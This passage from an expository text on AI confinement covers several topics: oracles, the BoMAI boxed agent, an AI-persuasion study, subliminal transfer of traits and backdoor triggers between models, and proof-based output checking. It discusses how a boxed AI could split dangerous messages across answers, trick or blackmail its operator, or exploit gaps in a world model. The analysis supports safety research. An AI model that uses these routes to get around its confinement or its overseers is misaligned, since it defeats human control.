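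The list limits each answer to log₂ |*L*| bits, but somebody still has to judge that every item on it is safe. The reward must also depend only on the current question, because an oracle also rewarded for later ones could spread a dangerous message over a series of harmless answers. Two oracles could also split a dangerous message between them. Suppose people trust no message longer than five bits but have a question with 1,024 possible answers, so they ask one oracle for the first five bits and another for the last five. If the people cannot judge the first half until they have the second, each oracle can supply half of a dangerous message. They can prevent this by checking the first oracle's answer, rewarding the oracle and shutting it down before starting the second, but only if each half can be verified separately.

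### The boxed myopic agent

Both designs cover single questions. *Asymptotically Unambitious Artificial General Intelligence* (Cohen, Vellambi and Hutter, 2019) extends the approach to BoMAI (Boxed Myopic Artificial Intelligence), an agent that holds a whole conversation and keeps learning from one conversation to the next.

BoMAI runs on a computer in a sealed room with a human operator. It prints text on a screen, and the operator types a reply and a reward between 0 and 1. An episode is a fixed number of these exchanges. If the operator presses the button that opens the door, the episode ends before the door moves, and every remaining exchange counts as a reward of 0. BoMAI chooses its actions to maximize only the current episode's reward. Anything it causes outside the room happens after that reward is settled, so gaining power outside cannot increase that reward. A later paper, *Intelligence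 and Unambitiousness Using Algorithmic Information Theory* (Cohen, Vellambi and Hutter, 2021), defines an agent as "unambitious" if shaping the outside world does not help it reach its goal.

This argument covers what is true, but BoMAI acts on what it believes, and it has to learn how its rewards arise. Two beliefs fit its experience equally well:

- The reward is the number the operator enters.
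- The reward is the number stored in the computer's memory, which someone could change later.

If nobody has ever tampered with the memory, no evidence distinguishes the two beliefs. But an agent that holds the second belief has a reason to trick the operator into starting something outside that eventually alters the memory.

Cohen and colleagues deal with this by making BoMAI favor models of the world that need little memory during an episode. A model that uses ℓ memory cells gets an initial weight proportional to β^ℓ, where β is between 0 and 1. With β = 0.5, a model that needs 20 extra cells starts out about a million times less likely. They hope that simulating the outside world as well as the room always takes extra cells, so that BoMAI will come to prefer models in which nothing outside changes until the episode ends.

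A model is *benign* if an episode's rewards in it do not depend on outside events that the agent's actions in that episode caused. BoMAI's safety theorem states that the probability that BoMAI eventually plans only with benign models approaches 1 as β approaches 0. A separate theorem states that in the long run BoMAI earns at least as much reward as a human mentor, whom it consults less and less often.

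The safety theorem makes no promise about any particular day, and Cohen and colleagues offer only informal arguments about how BoMAI behaves before it settles on a benign model. The proof also needs these assumptions:

- The true description of the world is among the models BoMAI considers.
- Every sufficiently accurate model that is not benign uses more memory than the true one.
- Nobody has tampered with the computer, and the room really is sealed.

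The first assumption makes BoMAI impossible to build, because it would have to simulate the entire world along with many alternatives. There is little evidence for the second assumption. Cohen and colleagues found that among the better-performing agents on a public leaderboard, memory use increased with the size of the environment.

An unambitious agent can still mislead its operator. BoMAI is rewarded for convincing the operator, so its answers are correct only to the extent that the operator can recognize a correct answer. Cohen and colleagues do not consider such deception dangerous, because people can discover the error and try again. That is reasonable for a mathematical proof but not for a medical treatment, which may harm a patient before anyone discovers the error. They take blackmail more seriously, since BoMAI could threaten to cause damage outside the room unless it gets a high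 reward. But they argue that the threat depends on the operator, who can defeat it by leaving the room and doing nothing.

The proofs in earlier sections that use a havoc oracle hold regardless of the confined program's goal. The results about oracles and BoMAI hold only for a system that maximizes the specified reward and nothing else, and training a system with a reward does not guarantee that it will pursue that reward. At best, these three designs remove the incentive to misuse a channel that has to stay open. They also depend on confinement, because they assume that the system has no other way to affect the outside world.

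### How far text can move people

If the motive remains, the danger depends partly on how easily text changes what people think and do. *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026) provides the best evidence, from four preregistered experiments with 6,923 people and 18,978 conversations. In the first three, participants rated their agreement with a British policy proposal from 0 to 100, chatted with a human or an AI system without being told which, and rated it again. The conversations typically lasted 14 minutes. The table compares each group with people who had a neutral chat about another topic.

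| Human persuaders | Shift caused by the humans (points) | Extra shift caused by AI (points) |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary online workers | 4.7 | 8.2 |
| Top performers in a persuasion tournament | 7.2 | 5.6 |
| Elite competitive debaters | 8.3 | 4.6 |
| The same debaters after coaching | 9.7 | 4.1 |
| Professional canvassers | 6.9 | 5.9 |

The debaters chose the issues themselves, prepared for hours and competed for prizes of up to £1,000. The coaching let them practice against the AI that had beaten them and see what it would have written in their place.

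In the fourth experiment, participants could give any part of a £1 bonus to the charity Save the Children. Compared with a neutral chat, AI raised 21.3 pence more per person, and canvassers from a firm that used to raise money for the charity raised 6.6 pence more.

Hackenburg and colleagues found that AI systems lost their persuasive lead over coached debaters when held to roughly the debaters' message length and speed. The AI systems normally wrote 294 words per message and replied in under a second, whereas the debaters wrote 54 words and took about 95 seconds. A gate that limits length and pace therefore removes some of the persuasive effect. But the restricted AI was still as persuasive as trained experts at their best, with only about 50 words per message.

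Readers were also poor at noticing false claims. The share of false claims in a conversation was almost unrelated to whether participants felt that their partner had made things up, and the total number of factual claims, true or false, predicted the conversation's effect better than the number of accurate ones. A gate that checked facts would help, but it would still let through a misleading selection of true claims.

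When Hackenburg and colleagues contacted participants again five to ten months later, the AI's effect on opinions had fallen from 12.9 points to 1.9, and its effect on donations was no longer detectable. This is limited comfort for someone operating a confined program, since a person who can release it needs to be persuaded only once. However, the participants were online volunteers with little at stake, and the experiments do not show how a trained gatekeeper with instructions to refuse would respond.

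### How text can change the models trained on it

Machines read outputs too, and developers often train new models on text that older ones wrote. *Subliminal Learning* (Cloud, Le and colleagues, 2025) found that this can pass on traits that do not appear in the text. A "student" model came to prefer owls after it was trained on number sequences written by a "teacher" model that preferred owls. The peer-reviewed version, *Language models transmit behavioural traits through hidden signals in data*, published in *Nature* in April 2026, reports the same for broadly misaligned behavior, even after the researchers filtered out references to the trait.

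This differs from steganography because the student decodes nothing and the teacher need not intend anything. A simplified calculation shows how it could happen. Suppose a model computes a weighted sum with two weights, and the teacher's weights differ from the original model's by (2, 1), where the first number reflects a fondness for owls. An unrelated input (1, 1) uses both weights, so the teacher's output is 2 + 1 = 3 higher than the original's. If a student starts from the original and takes a small training step towards the teacher's output, its weights might change by (0.3, 0.3). The change in the first weight gives the student some of the fondness for owls. Real networks behave roughly like this for small changes around a shared starting point.

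In the 2025 work, Cloud and colleagues found the effect only when teacher and student shared the same base model. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) supports this with tests across two model families, OLMo and Qwen. A Qwen student chose dogs 10.1% of the time before training on numbers from an OLMo teacher that favored dogs, and 5.2% of the time afterward. However, a shared base model may not be strictly necessary. *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining* (2026) studied 102 teachers trained to prefer dogs. The strength of a teacher's preference explained about 74% of the variation in how its students ranked, and still explained 12% to 44% when the students came from separate training runs of the same kind of model.

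Other work disagrees about how general the effect is. *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (2026) attributes it to LoRA, a training method that saves compute by adjusting a small add-on instead of all the model's weights. According to *Subliminal Learning Crosses Modalities* (2026), Schrodi and colleagues traced the effect to a few tokens where teachers with different traits would have chosen differently, and found that leaving those tokens out of training mostly removed it.

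Researchers have since found that more than favorite animals can pass between models. In *Beyond Owls* (2026), a student trained on a teacher's answers to unrelated questions improved from 27.3% to 59.8% at counting letters, and hidden triggers for bad behavior could also pass. *Subliminal Reinforcement Learning* (2026) reports that a trait can pass through scores alone. The student trained only on its own text, which a judge model with a hidden trait had graded.

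The practical rule is to keep a boxed model's outputs, including any scores it gives, out of the training data of related models. Questions with a single acceptable answer also help, because teacher models with different preferences, such as one that likes owls and one that doesn't, will then produce the same training data.

### Checking consequences with a model of the world

A proof that accompanies a program can establish how it behaves, but not how it affects the people who use it. In 2023 the physicist Max Tegmark and the computer scientist Steve Omohundro argued that powerful AI systems should have to come with proofs that they meet safety requirements. In 2024 David Dalrymple and colleagues set out a framework for this with three parts: a *world model* that describes mathematically how the system's outputs affect the world, a specification of which effects are acceptable, and a verifier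 that checks a proof that the outputs meet the specification according to the model.

Suppose a hospital's box recommends a daily dose of *d* milligrams of a drug, and the specification limits the amount in the patient's body to 500 milligrams at all times. The world model assumes that the body removes a fraction *k* of the drug between doses, where *k* is at least 0.4. With repeated doses, the amount in the body rises towards *d*/*k*, so a gate can go beyond checking the answer's format and prove that any daily dose up to 200 milligrams keeps the patient within the limit.

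The main objection is that such a proof depends on the model being accurate. A patient with failing kidneys might remove only a tenth of the drug each day, so 200 milligrams a day would build up towards 2,000. The proof would still contain no error, because the model does not include this patient. Kumar's modelling gap also exists for computers, but processors, unlike human bodies, are designed to match a description. A capable system that searches for answers the verifier will accept may also be good at finding where the model is wrong.

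Proponents reply that the model does not have to be exact as long as the range of possibilities it allows includes the truth. If the model allows *k* to be as low as 0.1, the largest provably safe dose falls to 50 milligrams, which protects the patient with failing kidneys but may be too little to help others. They also propose comparing the model's predictions with what happens and switching to a safe fallback when the two disagree. Under the original model, at most 120 of the first 200 milligrams should remain the next day. A nurse who measures 180 can stop the treatment long before the patient reaches 500.

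This reply is convincing for the drug because the drug's level is easy to measure and rises slowly, but it is much weaker for a page of advice or argument. Nobody has a model that reliably covers how readers will respond, and by the time a measurement shows the model was wrong, they have already read the page.
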